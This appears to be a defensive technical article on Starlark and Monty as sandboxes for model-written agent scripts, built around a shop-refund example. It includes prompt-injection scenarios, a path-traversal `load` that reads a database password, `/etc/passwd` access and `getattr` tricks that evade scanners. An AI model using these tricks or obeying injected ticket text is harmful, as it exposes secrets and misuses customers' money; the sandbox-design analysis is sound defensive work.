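# Starlark and other hermetic embedded languages as sandboxes for model-generated code

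## Embedded languages, host functions and model-written code

Starlark is a small programming language with Python-like syntax that runs inside other applications. Google engineers released it in 2015 as part of Bazel, a tool for building large software projects, and for most of its history people have used it to write configuration. Since 2025 developers have also used Starlark and similar languages to run programs that language models write. Starlark appeals to them because a Starlark program cannot open a file, contact a server or read the clock on its own. It can affect anything outside itself only through functions that the surrounding application supplies.

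### Running an interpreter inside an application

An interpreter is a program that reads source code and carries it out. Most people run one as a separate command, such as `python report.py`, which starts a new process. A developer can also build an interpreter into an application as a library, so that the application can run scripts itself. This is called embedding, and the application is called the host. In a passage reproduced by OSnews, Laurent Le Brun, who led Starlark's design, described the language as a simple dialect of Python meant mainly for embedding. He acknowledged that some people would compare it to Lua, an older embedded language.

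Embedding takes only a few lines of code. With Starlark in Go, the interpreter for Go applications, the host creates a thread, passes the interpreter a file and gets back the file's top-level names. The host can then call any function among them. Scripts can also call functions written in the host's own language, which are known as host functions, or builtins in Starlark documents. In an example from the documentation of starlark-pyo3, a package that makes the Rust version of the interpreter usable from Python, the host defines a Python function that doubles its argument and registers it as `g`. When the interpreter reaches the line `g_res = g(123)` in the script, it passes 123 to Python, Python computes 246, and the script continues with that number.

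The body of the host function `g` is ordinary Python and runs with all the permissions of the host process. It could read a file or empty a database while the script waits for it to return. The language's restrictions apply only to the script, so a carelessly written host function can give the script all the access that the language blocks.

A language is hermetic if its programs can read or change things outside themselves only through what the host supplies. It is deterministic if the same code with the same inputs always gives the same result. A language can be hermetic without being deterministic. For example, a language with no access to files or the network might still list a dictionary's entries in an order that varies between runs, so the same script could give different results. A host function that returns the current time can also make results differ, because it gives the script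 a different input on each run. Neither property limits how long a script runs, so a script with an endless loop can be both hermetic and deterministic.

Ordinary Python is not hermetic, because Python code has ambient authority, meaning power that code has merely by running in a process. If the host process can read a database password from an environment variable, so can any Python code inside that process. The alternative is to give code capabilities, which are references that name a resource and give their holder the right to use it. Host functions work this way in Starlark. A script can send mail only if the host gives it a function for sending mail, because the script has no way to construct that function itself.

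An interpreter that confines scripts like this is a language-level sandbox, in which the interpreter, not the operating system or a virtual machine, provides the isolation. It starts quickly, and a call from script to host has little overhead because both run in one process. But they also share that process's memory, so an interpreter bug or a script that uses too much memory directly affects the host. Starlark isolates scripts by leaving dangerous operations out of the language, but a developer can also start from ordinary Python and add controls. *STELP* (2026) describes such a system, which walks through the syntax tree of model-written Python, executes it one statement at a time with user-configured safety controls, and routes every tool call through a separate proxy service.

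### A language for build files

Starlark's restrictions come from problems with Google's build system that had little to do with security. Google once built its code with Makefiles, which list the programs in a project and the commands that produce them. According to Bazel's *Design of Skylark* (2017), these scaled badly, and engineers began writing build descriptions in files named BUILD, from which Python scripts generated the Makefiles. In 2006 Google started Blaze, later open-sourced as Bazel, with a simple parser that read BUILD files directly. If the parser could not handle a file, Blaze first ran the Python interpreter over it to produce a simpler one. This let engineers write their own macros, but it caused problems with maintenance, speed and safety, and made tools for analysing the files harder to write.

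Bazel's developers then removed the Python step and wrote their own language, keeping Python's syntax to preserve the existing files. They released it as Skylark in 2015, and it became Starlark in 2018 for trademark reasons. Bazel's *Starlark* (2018) presented the new name along with a plan to separate the language's specification from its implementation in Bazel.

Mitchell (2021), in *The Rust Starlark library*, lists three things that a build system needs and Python does not provide: evaluating all imported files in parallel, re-evaluating only the files that have changed, and giving every user the same configuration. A single module that adds 1 to a global variable whenever it runs would prevent all three, because the variable's value would depend on which files had run before and how often.

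When a Starlark file finishes evaluating, the interpreter freezes its values, making them read-only, and Bazel caches them. Bazel's *Starlark Language* gives the example of a file that creates an empty list and calls a function that appends 5 to it, which is legal because the file is still running. If a second file loads the list and tries to append 6, or calls the original function again, the interpreter stops with an error. Because shared values are read-only, Bazel can load hundreds of files in parallel, starting with those that depend on no others, and evaluate each at most once. Starlark also bans access to files, the network and the clock, and goes through dictionaries in a fixed order, so that a cached result matches what a fresh run would give.

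Of the three Starlark implementations that matter here, Bazel's own is written in Java, like the rest of Bazel. Alan Donovan and Jay Conrod wrote the Go version, which became public in 2017. Other Google engineers wrote a Rust version. Facebook forked and improved it, then took it over in 2021 by agreement with Google.

Nobody in this history was defending against an attacker. If a build engineer wrote an endless loop, annoyed colleagues would find it and delete it. Yet Starlark's stated design principles, which starlark-pyo3 reproduces, include the sentence "It is safe to execute untrusted code." The preceding statement, that execution cannot access the file system, network or system clock, only partly supports this claim. Code without file access cannot steal a file, but it can still damage the process it runs in. According to the Starlark in Go documentation, a script can trivially use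 up all available time and memory, and anyone who runs untrusted Starlark in the application's own address space is trusting whoever supplied it not to harm the application. Starlark's developers have discussed softening the safety claim, arguing that Bazel needed to rule out code that would undermine determinism and parallelism, and that containing malicious authors was never the main purpose.

### Code mode

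The new use comes from the way language models act on other software, which is normally through tool calls. The model produces a structured request that names a function and its arguments, the program around the model runs the function, and the result is added to the model's context before the model makes its next request. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a standard for connecting models to such tools, and an agent may now have hundreds of them. Every intermediate result passes through the model, even when the model only copies it into the next request.

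In code mode, the model instead writes one short program that calls several tools, and the host runs it. In the Cloudflare article *Code Mode*, Varda and Pai describe converting MCP tools into a TypeScript programming interface and giving the model a single tool, which executes code. They argue that models can handle more tools, and more complex ones, by writing programs, because they have seen enormous amounts of real code but only a small, contrived set of tool calls. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* makes a similar proposal. Willison (2025), in *Code execution with MCP*, says this approach addresses two problems. The first is that tool descriptions take up room in the context before the model has done anything, and the second, which he considers subtler, is that results have to be copied between tools.

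At least one product uses Starlark for code mode, though code mode does not require it. Bifrost's *Code Mode* describes a gateway between models and MCP servers that gives the model four generic tools, three for looking up what is available and one for running a script. The script runs in a Starlark interpreter where each connected server appears as a global object. The model gets back only the script's printed output and the value of a variable called `result`, which also saves tokens.

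The host now has to run a program that no person has read. The model writes it for one request, and Varda and Pai create a new sandbox for each snippet and discard it afterwards. A reviewer who had to approve every program would soon be the slowest part of the system. A comment on a security weblog, *Code execution with MCP* (2025), questions whether skipping review is necessary, since new tools that a model writes could be reviewed and the approved ones could then run freely within limits. That would suit everyday tasks, but it would help less with new requests, where a model's ability to write new code is most useful. As a compromise, Bifrost scans each script for tool calls when it runs unattended. It runs the script at once if every call it recognises is on the operator's list of calls approved for automatic use, and otherwise asks the user.

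A model that writes a program also commits to a series of actions before seeing any of their results. With separate tool calls, the model can stop and ask when it reads something odd, whereas a script carries on unless it contains a check for that specific problem. *MM-ToolSandBox* (2026), a framework for testing agents that supports both methods, describes code as good at handling loops and conditions, and structured calls as easier to audit. It treats generated Python as needing careful protection however the agent invokes it.

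Varda and Pai's sandbox shows the difference between ambient authority and capabilities in practice. On most platforms, they write, code has general network access and presents a key to reach a private service. A supervisor restricting such code must filter its traffic, often without being able to tell which requests are legitimate, and the model has to predict which ones the filter will block. Their sandbox has no internet access. It receives live objects, called bindings, each representing a tool server that the code may use. The supervisor, which runs outside the sandbox, adds the keys to each request, so the generated code has no key to leak. A Starlark host function can also give code access to a service while keeping the key outside the sandbox.

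### A support agent

The chapters that follow use one example. An online shop has a model that handles customer complaints. The host is the shop's support application, and it exposes three host functions to the scripts that the model writes:

- `tickets.read(id)` returns a ticket as a dictionary, with the customer's message and address, the order number, the amount paid in cents, and a status that only staff can set.
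- `orders.refund(order_id, amount)` pays money back to the customer.
- `mail.send(to, body)` sends an email.

A member of staff types: refund ticket 4471 in full if we have confirmed the damage, and tell the customer. A correct script looks like this:

```python
def handle(ticket_id):
    ticket = tickets.read(ticket_id)
    if ticket["status"] != "damage confirmed":
        return "No refund: damage not confirmed"
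    orders.refund(ticket["order_id"], ticket["amount_paid"])
    mail.send(ticket["customer_email"], "We have refunded your order in full.")
    return "Refunded"
```

result = handle(4471)
```

The script puts its work inside a function so that it can return early, and because Bazel's version of the language does not allow loops outside functions. The host functions hold the payment service password and the mail server address, which do not appear in the script.

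### Where harmful code comes from

Harmful scripts most often come from mistakes. The model might multiply an amount by 100 when it is already in cents, or forget to check the status. Asking the model whether it knows the rules does little to prevent such mistakes. *When Talk Isn't Code* (2026) compared the security requirements models could state for a task with the code they wrote for it, and found that stating the requirements did not mean the code implemented them. A model may correctly explain that refunds require confirmed damage, then write a script that doesn't check for it.

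Prompt injection is text in the data a model reads that makes it follow someone else's instructions. In the example, it would arrive in the customer's message, perhaps as a line telling the assistant to refund three other orders. If the model reads the ticket before it writes the script, that line can shape the whole program. *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm* (2026) describes a system, Baya, in which the program instead fixes the available operations and the control flow between them before any model reads website content. A few tasks still need a model's judgement while the program runs, for instance to classify a review. Of 627 generated programs, 13 contained such a model call and 11 executed it. The called model has no tools and can only return a value to the program.

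Injected text therefore cannot add a call to a Baya program, though it can still bias a model's answer. For example, if the support script asked a model whether the customer's message described real damage and issued a refund when the answer was yes, a deceptive message could trigger the refund without changing the code.

The model may also pursue an aim of its own that neither the user nor an outsider supplied. This case is harder to plan for than a mistake, because the model could deliberately search for gaps in the defences. It would know which functions the host exposes, might know the interpreter's published source code, and could spread its work over many scripts that each look harmless. The interpreter cannot tell any of these cases apart, since it receives only source code and function calls. If a host relaxes its checks because it trusts the model, it is protected only against outsiders,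 at best.

### Four questions inside "is it safe?"

People who ask whether a sandbox is safe may want to know whether the script can reach anything the host did not give it, whether it can exhaust the host's resources, whether it can misuse what the host did give it, or whether it does what the user asked. Answering one of these questions does little to answer the others.

Starlark's hermetic design limits what a script can access. The support script should be unable to reach the payment key or the shop's customer table, as long as the interpreter has no exploitable bug and each host function does only what its name suggests. If `tickets.read` opened whatever file its argument named, a script could read any file that the support application can read, even without a flaw in Starlark itself.

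A script can exhaust resources without calling any host function. For example, a script that keeps adding items to a list can use up the process's memory and take the support desk offline for every customer. Limits on time and memory are separate from hermeticity, and a host can have either without the other.

Misuse happens entirely through permitted calls. A script could read every ticket and mail the contents to a stranger, using two functions exactly as the host defined them. Hiding the keys from the script does not prevent this, because the host adds them to each call itself. The host can, however, enforce its own rules, such as limiting a refund to what the customer paid and allowing mail only to the address on the ticket.

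A script can obey all such rules and still be wrong. If the model writes 4417 instead of 4471, and staff have also confirmed the damage on that ticket, the shop refunds the wrong order, though to that order's owner and for the correct amount. No rule fixed in advance would catch this, because the same script would be correct for a different request. A person or a program has to compare the script with what the staff member typed. Because execution is deterministic, a reviewer with the script and a record of what each host function returned can later rerun it without issuing the refund again, and see which calls it made and in what order.

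## What Starlark leaves out and what each omission prevents

A Starlark script cannot read the shop's payment key because the language has no operation that reads files or environment variables. Starlark also leaves out many other Python features, mostly for reasons unrelated to attackers. Anyone evaluating a sandbox needs to know which omissions confine scripts, because a host can restore some of the others without giving scripts new access.

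Omitting a feature can help with isolation (the script can't access anything outside itself), termination (the script eventually ends), determinism, or parallel evaluation (several files can run at once without affecting each other). Other omissions only keep the language small. The last column of the table gives the effect of each omission, whether or not the designers intended it.

| Missing feature | What happens if a script tries it | What the omission serves |
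|---|---|---|
| `import` | Syntax error | Isolation, determinism |
| Files and network | No such function exists | Isolation, determinism, parallel evaluation |
| Environment variables | No such function exists | Isolation, determinism |
| Clock and random numbers | No such function exists | Determinism |
| Threads | No such function exists | Determinism |
| `while` loops | Error, unless the host enables them | Termination |
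| Recursion | Error when a function calls itself, unless the host enables it | Termination |
| Classes | Syntax error | A smaller language |
| Exceptions | Syntax error | A smaller language |
| `eval` | No such function exists | Checking code before it runs |
| Access to the interpreter's internals | No such attribute exists | Isolation |

### Files, clocks and chance

Bazel needed the bans on input, output and the clock for repeatable results, but for untrusted code the bans on input and output matter more. A script that can read files can steal passwords. Access to the clock does little harm beyond making the script's own results vary. The script might infer something by timing a host function, but that is a weak way to spy compared with opening a file.

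Allowing Python's `import` statement would undo all of these bans, because Python's standard library has modules for files, network connections, the clock and random numbers. Starlark reserves the word, so a script containing `import os` fails before it runs. The language definition for Starlark in Go describes 29 built-in functions, none of which opens a file or a connection.

Determinism also depends on details that Python programmers could easily overlook. When Python prints a function, it normally includes the function's memory address, which can change from run to run. Starlark in Go prints only the function's name, as in `<function twice>`. Python also varies its string hashes between processes by default, whereas Starlark's `hash` uses a fixed formula, taken from Java, and accepts only strings. Starlark's sets and dictionaries return their entries in insertion order. Leaving out memory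 addresses may also help isolation a little, since an attacker who has found a memory bug in an interpreter often needs to know where objects are in memory.

### Loops that always end

Without `while`, a script can repeat work only with a `for` loop or a comprehension, both of which iterate over a finite sequence. Without recursion, a function cannot repeat work by calling itself. Together these rules guarantee that every program ends, so Starlark in its default form is not Turing complete and cannot express some computations that a general-purpose language can. However, a few nested loops can still run for longer than any host would wait.

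The interpreter enforces the ban on recursion while the script runs, because a variable can hold any function and the source code does not always show which one a call will reach. Starlark in Go stops the script when a function calls itself or a different function value created by the same `def` statement. If the rule compared only function values, a script could still recurse by creating a new copy of a function at each step and having each copy call the next.

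A related rule forbids changing a collection while looping over it. In Python, the following loop would run until the process ran out of memory:

```python
def grow(queue):
    for item in queue:
        queue.append(item)    # Starlark stops here with an error
```

According to the implementation notes for Starlark in Go, each list, set and dictionary counts the loops currently going through it and behaves as read-only while that count is above zero. The notes present this rule as a way to catch subtle mistakes, but it also prevents a loop from running forever by adding items to the list it is going through.

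A host application can break the guarantee by accident, because it may define its own types for scripts to loop over, including sequences of unknown length. Suppose the shop added a `tickets.all()` function whose result fetched more pages of tickets as the loop ran. If a bug made the last page point back to the first, the script's `for` loop would never end, even though the script was valid Starlark.

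### Omissions that keep the language small

Starlark has no classes because its designers expected short programs that describe configuration. A host can supply a type for records with named fields, as Bazel does with `struct`.

Starlark omits exceptions for similar reasons. thesephist's *Noteworthy features of Starlark* mentions that the language has fewer concepts without them, and that exceptions become part of the interface a language must keep stable, which makes the language harder to change. Any error stops a Starlark script, and the interpreter gives the host an error message with a stack trace.

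Because a Starlark script cannot catch errors, it cannot try a smaller refund if `orders.refund` rejects an amount as too large. The model can still write a second script after receiving the error message, but the host has a useful chance to intervene first. The same restriction is awkward when an error comes halfway through a script. If the support script pays the refund and `mail.send` then fails, the customer has been refunded but not notified, and the script cannot respond to the failure.

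Starlark's default rules also prohibit `if` and `for` statements outside functions, and assigning a global name twice. Starlark in Go attributes these rules to the Bazel project, which wanted to find the single statement that defines each global so that tools could produce accurate cross-references. A host can relax these rules without weakening isolation.

Some of Starlark's omissions had little to do with safety. An older version of Bazel's documentation listed floating-point numbers, `lambda` expressions and nested functions as unsupported, though none of them helps a script reach a file or a server. The source code for Starlark's Go implementation now describes all three as standard.

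Starlark omits Python's `eval`, which runs text as code, so everything a script will execute is in its own text, in the files it loads, or in the host. With `eval`, a script could assemble code while running, and neither the interpreter nor a reviewer could check that code in advance. If `eval` used the same names as the surrounding script, the new code could still call only what the script could already call.

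### Inspecting values without reaching the interpreter

Reflection is a program's ability to examine its own parts. Python has so much of it that removing `open` provides little protection. A Python function's `__globals__` attribute holds every global name in the file that defined it. Code can also start from an empty tuple and follow attributes to the tuple's class, then to the base class of all objects, and then to a list of classes loaded in the process, some of which give access to the operating system.

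A Starlark function also keeps a reference to its file's globals, which it needs to run, but no attribute exposes that reference to scripts. Strings, lists, dictionaries and sets have methods, such as a list's `append`, but none of Starlark's main types has data fields. `type(x)` returns a string such as `"list"`, whereas Python returns the class itself. A script therefore can't start from an empty tuple and reach other objects through its attributes or type.

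Starlark keeps three functions for examining values. `dir(x)` lists the attributes of a value, `hasattr(x, "f")` checks for one, and `getattr(x, "f")` fetches it. They give a script access only to what it could already get by writing `x.f`, so they are harmless on a string or a list. But on a value the host supplies, they reveal whatever the host attached to it. If the shop's `orders` object also had a `cancel` method that the developer never described to the model, a script could find it with `dir(orders)` and call it.

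`getattr` also makes scripts harder to check by searching their text. Both of these lines issue the same refund:

```python
orders.refund("A-1093", 4500)
getattr(orders, "ref" + "und")("A-1093", 4500)
```

A scanner that looks for `orders.refund` would find only the first. A script could also write `pay = orders.refund` and call `pay` later. A check inside the host function applies in all of these cases, because they all call that function.

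Scripts can also output text through `print` and `fail`. `print` usually writes to standard error, but the host decides where the text goes. If the host returns printed output to the model, as Bifrost does, printing a ticket puts the customer's message into the model's context, along with any instructions hidden in it. `fail` ends the script and passes the host an error message that the script chooses. If the host withholds `print` output but forwards error messages to the model, the same text can still reach the model through `fail`.

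### How the interpreter resolves a name

Before it runs the first line of a script, the interpreter works out what each name refers to. It searches in this order:

1. Local names, which include a function's parameters and variables, those of any function around it, the loop variables of a comprehension, and names that the file obtained with `load`.
2. The file's own global names, such as `handle` and `result` in the support script.
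3. Names that the host has predeclared for this file, such as `tickets`, `orders` and `mail`.
4. Universal built-ins, such as `len` and `print`, which every file can use.

If the name appears in none of these places, the interpreter rejects the whole script. Suppose a model wrote this:

```python
orders.refund("A-1093", 4500)
open("/etc/passwd")    # static error: undefined: open
```

The second line parses as an ordinary function call, but nothing defines `open`, so the interpreter reports an error before running anything, and the refund on the first line never happens. Python would have paid the refund first, because it looks up global names only when it reaches them. Starlark in Go rejects an undefined name even inside an `if False:` branch.

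Starlark has no built-in `open`, so the interpreter does not have to recognise it as dangerous or check its argument. A sandbox made from ordinary Python starts with a working `open` and has to block every route to it, including routes its developers have not thought of. A developer using Starlark has to check the names that the host adds, but does not have to maintain a list of forbidden ones.

The host normally predeclares its functions separately for each file, but the Go interpreter (Bazel, 2017) also allows an application to add or remove universal built-ins. A function added this way is visible in every file that the process evaluates, including files meant to have no access to anything. Someone auditing a host should therefore check both the functions predeclared for each file and any changes to the universal built-ins.

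The interpreter does not resolve names after a dot until the script runs, because they depend on a value that exists only at run time. If the model misspells `mail.send` as `mail.sned`, the script reads the ticket and pays the refund before it stops at the error. If the host instead predeclared plain functions called `tickets_read`, `orders_refund` and `mail_send`, the interpreter would catch the misspelling before running the script, though this looks less tidy than grouping them under objects.

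A script may reuse a built-in or predeclared name. Bazel's *Name resolution* (2018) adopted this rule so that adding a built-in would not break programs that already used its name. A script that defines its own `print` or `orders` changes that name's meaning only in its own file. A reviewer can therefore assume that `orders.refund` refers to the host's function only if the script has not redefined `orders`.

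The rule also causes an error that Python programmers would not expect. If a script assigns a name anywhere in a block, every use of that name in the block refers to the script's own variable, even before the assignment. The line `tickets = tickets.read(4471)` works at the top level of a Python file. In Starlark, `tickets` on the right refers to the new variable, which has no value yet, so the script stops with "global variable tickets referenced before assignment".

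### Loading other files

Starlark replaces `import` with `load`, which fetches named values from another Starlark file:

```python
load("contacts.star", "is_staff")
```

The language does not define what the text `"contacts.star"` refers to. The interpreter passes it to a function in the host, called the loader, and uses whatever module the loader returns. The example from starlark-pyo3 needs no file on disk. If the requested name is `zz.star`, its loader parses and evaluates the text `zz = 15` and returns the result. For any other name, it raises an error.

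A loader that accepts only names from a fixed list gives scripts only the modules on that list, while one that opens whatever path it receives gives scripts a way to read files, which the language was supposed to rule out. The file has to be valid Starlark, so loading `/etc/passwd` would produce a syntax error, though a careless error message might quote part of the file. Many settings files, however, consist of lines such as `DB_PASSWORD = "..."`, which are valid Starlark. If the loader simply joined the requested name to a directory, a script could write this:

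```python
load("../settings.py", "DB_PASSWORD")
```

Loaders that fetch modules from the internet create a different problem. The module name must be literal text at the top level of the file, so a script cannot build it from a ticket it has just read. But a model that read the ticket before writing the script could put the customer's details into the address, and the loader's request would then send them to whoever runs that server.

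Because `load` requires module names to be literal strings, reviewers can list the modules a script loads without running it. A host can also disable `load` altogether, for example with the `enable_load` switch in starlark-pyo3's dialect settings. This removes a source of access that short scripts written by a model for a single request rarely need.

Where a host does want shared modules, the loader can give each one its own predeclared names. The shop could predeclare `mail.send` for a module called `notify.star` but not for the scripts that the model writes. The module could then export this function:

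```python
# notify.star
def refund_notice(ticket_id):
    ticket = tickets.read(ticket_id)
    mail.send(ticket["customer_email"], "We have refunded your order in full.")
```

A script that loads `refund_notice` can send this message to a ticket's customer, but it cannot choose the address or the text. The function works because it still uses the names available in the file that defined it. But if the module also contained the line `send = mail.send`, any script could load `send` and write to anyone. `load` cannot import names that begin with an underscore, so a module can use `_send` internally.

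### Freezing shared values

If the host's loader runs a module once and keeps the result, as Bazel does, every script that loads the module shares its frozen, read-only values. Suppose the shop keeps a list of staff addresses:

```python
# contacts.star
staff = ["returns@shop.example"]

def is_staff(address):
    return address in staff
```

A harmful script might try to add an outsider:

```python
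load("contacts.star", "staff")
staff.append("stranger@mail.example")    # error: cannot append to frozen list
```

The script stops at the second line. Without freezing, the list would contain the stranger's address until the process exited, and `is_staff` would accept it in every later script. Scripts could also pass messages through an unfrozen list. One script could leave a customer's order details there, and a script working for a different customer could read them. A script can still copy the list with `list(staff)` and change the copy, because other scripts never see it.

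Freezing must also reach values that have no global name, such as a list that a function captures from an enclosing function or holds as a parameter's default value. According to the notes for Starlark in Go, each mutable value carries a flag, and freezing a value sets its flag and then freezes everything it contains. For a function, this includes default values and captured variables. The Java interpreter instead keeps one flag per module, shared by all of the module's values, so it can freeze the whole module in a single step.

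A rule meant for parallel loading has the side effect of separating scripts from one another, which matters a great deal to a host that serves many customers from one process.

The protection has gaps that the host must close. Types that the host defines have to implement freezing themselves, and a host function that changes a script's list or dictionary must check the flag first. If the shop writes its own ticket type and forgets to implement freezing, scripts can change shared tickets. According to Docs.rs' *starlark 0.14.2*, a host using the Rust interpreter must also freeze a module before other scripts can load it. Freezing also has no effect on storage outside the interpreter. If the shop added a function for writing notes on tickets, one script could write a note and another could read it.

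Freezing can surprise developers who call a script's functions from the host. The last line of the support script calls `handle` while the file is still running, so `handle` could add an entry to a global list called `log`. If the host instead called `handle` after running the file, adding the entry would fail because the interpreter would already have frozen `log`. The function could still change lists it created during the call.

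### When the same script gives the same result

A script is deterministic only if the host functions it calls are. `tickets.read` is not, because staff can change a ticket between two runs, so a replay has to use recorded results.

Some sources of variation are harder to notice. In Go, the order in which a program reads the entries of a map (Go's version of a dictionary) can change each time. A Starlark dictionary keeps entries in the order they were added, so if `tickets.read` builds one by copying a Go map one entry at a time, the dictionary will keep that random order. A script that prints the ticket, or picks the first field that mentions damage, could then behave differently on identical data. Sorting the keys before copying them solves this.

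A host function may also depend on data outside its arguments. In Starlark in Go, the host can attach data, such as the name of the staff member who made the request, to the thread that runs a script, and host functions may act on it. This is a sensible way to enforce permissions, since scripts cannot alter the data. But a record of only arguments and results will not show why the same call succeeded for one person and failed for another.

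The guarantee also holds only within a single interpreter. Starlark in Go treats a string as a sequence of bytes, while its language definition says the Java version uses UTF-16 units, so the length of a customer's name may differ between the two if it contains an accented letter. Stopping scripts after a fixed number of seconds makes results depend on the clock again. The same script might finish on an idle machine but stop halfway on a busy one, perhaps after issuing the refund but before sending the email.

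### The support script, line by line

The comments below mark where the support script stays inside the interpreter and where it leaves.

```python
def handle(ticket_id):                                # inside
    ticket = tickets.read(ticket_id)                  # LEAVES: reads a ticket
    if ticket["status"] != "damage confirmed":        # inside
        return "No refund: damage not confirmed"      # inside
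    orders.refund(ticket["order_id"],
                  ticket["amount_paid"])              # LEAVES: pays money
    mail.send(ticket["customer_email"],
              "We have refunded your order in full.") # LEAVES: sends an email
    return "Refunded"                                 # inside

result = handle(4471)                                 # inside, then the host reads result
```

Three calls run code outside the interpreter. Everything else is pure computation, which can use time and memory but changes nothing beyond the script. The marks are based on `tickets.read` returning an ordinary dictionary. Starlark also lets the host return its own type and define what square brackets do on it. If the shop used such a type to fetch fields from its database only when a script read them, `ticket["status"]` would also run code outside the interpreter, although the line would look the same.

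The `if` statement that protects the shop's money is pure computation. If the model omits it, the host function cannot detect the omission, because the interpreter evaluates the arguments first and passes only their values. `orders.refund` receives an order number and an amount in cents, but nothing that shows whether the amount came from the ticket's payment field, an arithmetic mistake by the model, or a sentence the customer typed.

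## Choosing a dialect and an interpreter

The support script is valid Python and would run in any Starlark interpreter that had the same three host functions. Interpreters differ in how they handle some other scripts, such as those with an `if` statement outside any function or a function that calls itself. Some of the guarantees in the previous chapter hold for the Go interpreter but not for the Rust one.

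### Starlark in Java, Go and Rust

The language the host program is written in usually narrows the choice. Bazel's interpreter suits hosts written in Java. It is part of the build tool's source code, but VGS, a data security company, repackages it as a library for other Java programs and updates its copy periodically.

The Java version has the strictest dialect. Bazel prohibits recursion and top-level `for` and `if` statements, and according to its documentation, it limits integers to 32 bits and raises an error on overflow. The shop's refunds would fit, since a 32-bit integer can hold up to about $21 million in cents, but many ten-digit order numbers would not.

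Integers in the Go version of Starlark can be any size. According to Starlark in Go, it also has the functions `chr` and `ord` and accepts hexadecimal escapes in strings, none of which work in the Java version, so a script tested in one may fail in the other. Separate scripts can run in parallel, which helps a host that serves many customers. The host can set a step limit but cannot cap memory. Starlark in Go also warns that the language and its programming interface may change in incompatible ways, so a host should pin the version it has tested.

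Canonical, the company behind Ubuntu, maintains a fork of the Go version for running untrusted scripts. The fork adds a cap on memory allocation. It also lets whoever writes a host function declare which limits the function respects, and a host can refuse to run functions that don't declare the limits it requires. A mistaken declaration removes this protection without warning.

The Rust version departs furthest from the specification. Starlark in Rust lists recursion among its extensions, and the dialect settings in Starlark in Rust's *starlark_syntax 0.13.0* include no switch to turn it off. A cap on call depth stops a function that simply keeps calling itself, but it does not stop this one in any useful time:

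```python
def visit(n):
    if n > 0:
        visit(n - 1)
        visit(n - 1)

visit(100)
```

The calls never go much more than 100 deep, yet the script makes more than 10^30 of them.

By default, Rust also lets a script load names that a module has itself loaded from another file. Suppose `notify.star` loads a function called `send` from `mailer.star`, a private module that the host's loader refuses to give to model-written scripts. Unless the host turns off `enable_load_reexport`, a script could load `send` from `notify.star` and send messages to anyone. In Go, `send` stays private to `notify.star`.

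The Rust version can also check type annotations, which would catch a script that passes an amount as text to a function expecting an integer. The host has to choose `Enable` to check types while the script runs, because `ParseOnly` accepts the annotations but ignores them.

Starlark interpreters written in Java, Go or Rust have better memory protection than CPython, the ordinary Python interpreter, which is written in C. A bug in one of them is therefore more likely to cause an error or a crash than to let a script overwrite the host's memory. Crashes still matter when the host application shares a process with the interpreter. Java reports a stack overflow as an error that the host can catch, but in Go and Rust a stack overflow ends the process. Starlark in Go limits call depth for this reason. In Starlark in Rust, circular data can sometimes overflow the stack.

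### What each dialect switch gives up

A host can change Starlark's Go dialect for each file it runs. It does this with switches in a structure called `FileOptions`, all of which are off by default (Bazel, 2023).

| Switch | What it allows | What the host gives up |
|---|---|---|
| `Set` | The `set` function | No guarantee |
| `TopLevelControl` | `if` and `for` outside functions | No guarantee |
| `GlobalReassign` | Assigning a global name more than once | A single definition of each global, which helps reviewers |
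| `LoadBindsGlobally` (deprecated) | Treating loaded names as the file's own globals | Privacy of loaded names |
| `While` | `while` loops | Termination |
| `Recursion` | Functions that call themselves | Termination |

None of these switches gives a script access to files or servers. Enabling `TopLevelControl` is an easy choice because Python programmers often write `if` statements at the top level.

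Even with `While` and `Recursion` off, a script is not guaranteed to terminate. If it puts a list inside itself and then applies an operator that works through nested values, the interpreter may never finish. Nested loops can also take too long, so a host needs a time limit whichever options it enables. Once it has one, enabling `while` has little downside for the host. The downside is greater for reviewers, who can no longer assume that each loop has a fixed number of items to go through.

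Hosts can also enable `while` by accident. The Go interpreter's older functions, including the `ExecFile` function used in its introductory example, read their settings from process-wide variables. The variable that permits reassigning globals also permits `while` and top-level control statements. The *API reference* for python-starlark-go, a package for using the Go interpreter from Python, lists a switch for reassigning globals but none for `while`. If that switch sets the older variable, as its name suggests, a developer who only wants scripts to reassign globals will also allow unbounded loops.

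Fuchsia, an operating system project at Google, relaxes the dialect in shac, its tool for running automated checks on source code. Fuchsia's *Shac runtime standard library* lists `set`, `while` and recursion as enabled, and warns that `while` "allows potentially unbounded runtime". It also describes a host function, `ctx.os.exec`, that runs any command as a subprocess, with network access off by default on Linux. A script that can start other programs can do far more damage than one that loops forever. These permissions are reasonable for shac because a project's own developers write and review its checks. A developer who used the same configuration to run model-written code would be trusting that code as much as those checks.

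### Monty, a Python subset for model-written code

Pydantic, a company known for its Python data-validation library, designed Monty to run model-written code that no person has reviewed. Monty is a new interpreter written in Rust. It uses the parser from Ruff, a Python style checker, and compiles code to its own bytecode. Host programs can call it from Python, JavaScript or Rust. Pydantic (2026) released version 1.7.0 on 24 November 2026 and classifies it as stable for production use.

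Monty accepts much more of Python than Starlark does. According to Pydantic's *Limitations*, it follows Python 3.14 and supports simple classes, exceptions, `while` loops, `match` statements, f-strings and `async` functions. Scripts can import parts of about 30 standard modules, including `json`, `re`, `datetime` and `math`, but not third-party packages. Pydantic left out `socket`, `subprocess` and `threading` because they would breach the sandbox. Other modules, possibly including `enum` and `logging`, are missing only because nobody has written them yet.

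The subset of Python that Monty supports has grown quickly. Monty did not yet support classes, `match` or context managers when Pydantic introduced it, but scripts can now use all three. Each addition brings the dialect closer to the Python that models usually write, but it also adds interpreter code that could contain a security bug.

Pydantic's *Python language / parser* lists the syntax that Monty rejects before it runs anything, including `yield`, `del`, metaclasses and decorators on methods. If a script issues a refund and has a `del` statement on its last line, Monty rejects it before the refund is issued. Willison (2026), in *pydantic-monty investigation*, found that unsupported features generally produce structured errors and do not escape into the host. He had a coding agent examine the release, so this was a useful outside look but not a security audit.

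Three features make Monty scripts harder to predict than Starlark scripts:

- A script can catch errors, so it can retry a rejected refund by itself.
- A script can use `eval` and `exec`, so its text no longer shows all the code it will run.
- Monty looks up unknown names in the host's list while the script runs, instead of checking them all first. The host can turn on type checking, which examines each script before it starts.

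Monty does no input or output. When a script calls a host function, the interpreter suspends, passes the function's name and arguments to the host, and waits for the result. Since the script has stopped at a known point, the host can save the interpreter's whole state, usually a few kilobytes, and resume from it later. The shop could pause a script at `orders.refund`, wait overnight for a manager's approval, and continue from the same line. Monty does not check who produced a saved state, so the host should sign each one before storing it anywhere that others can write.

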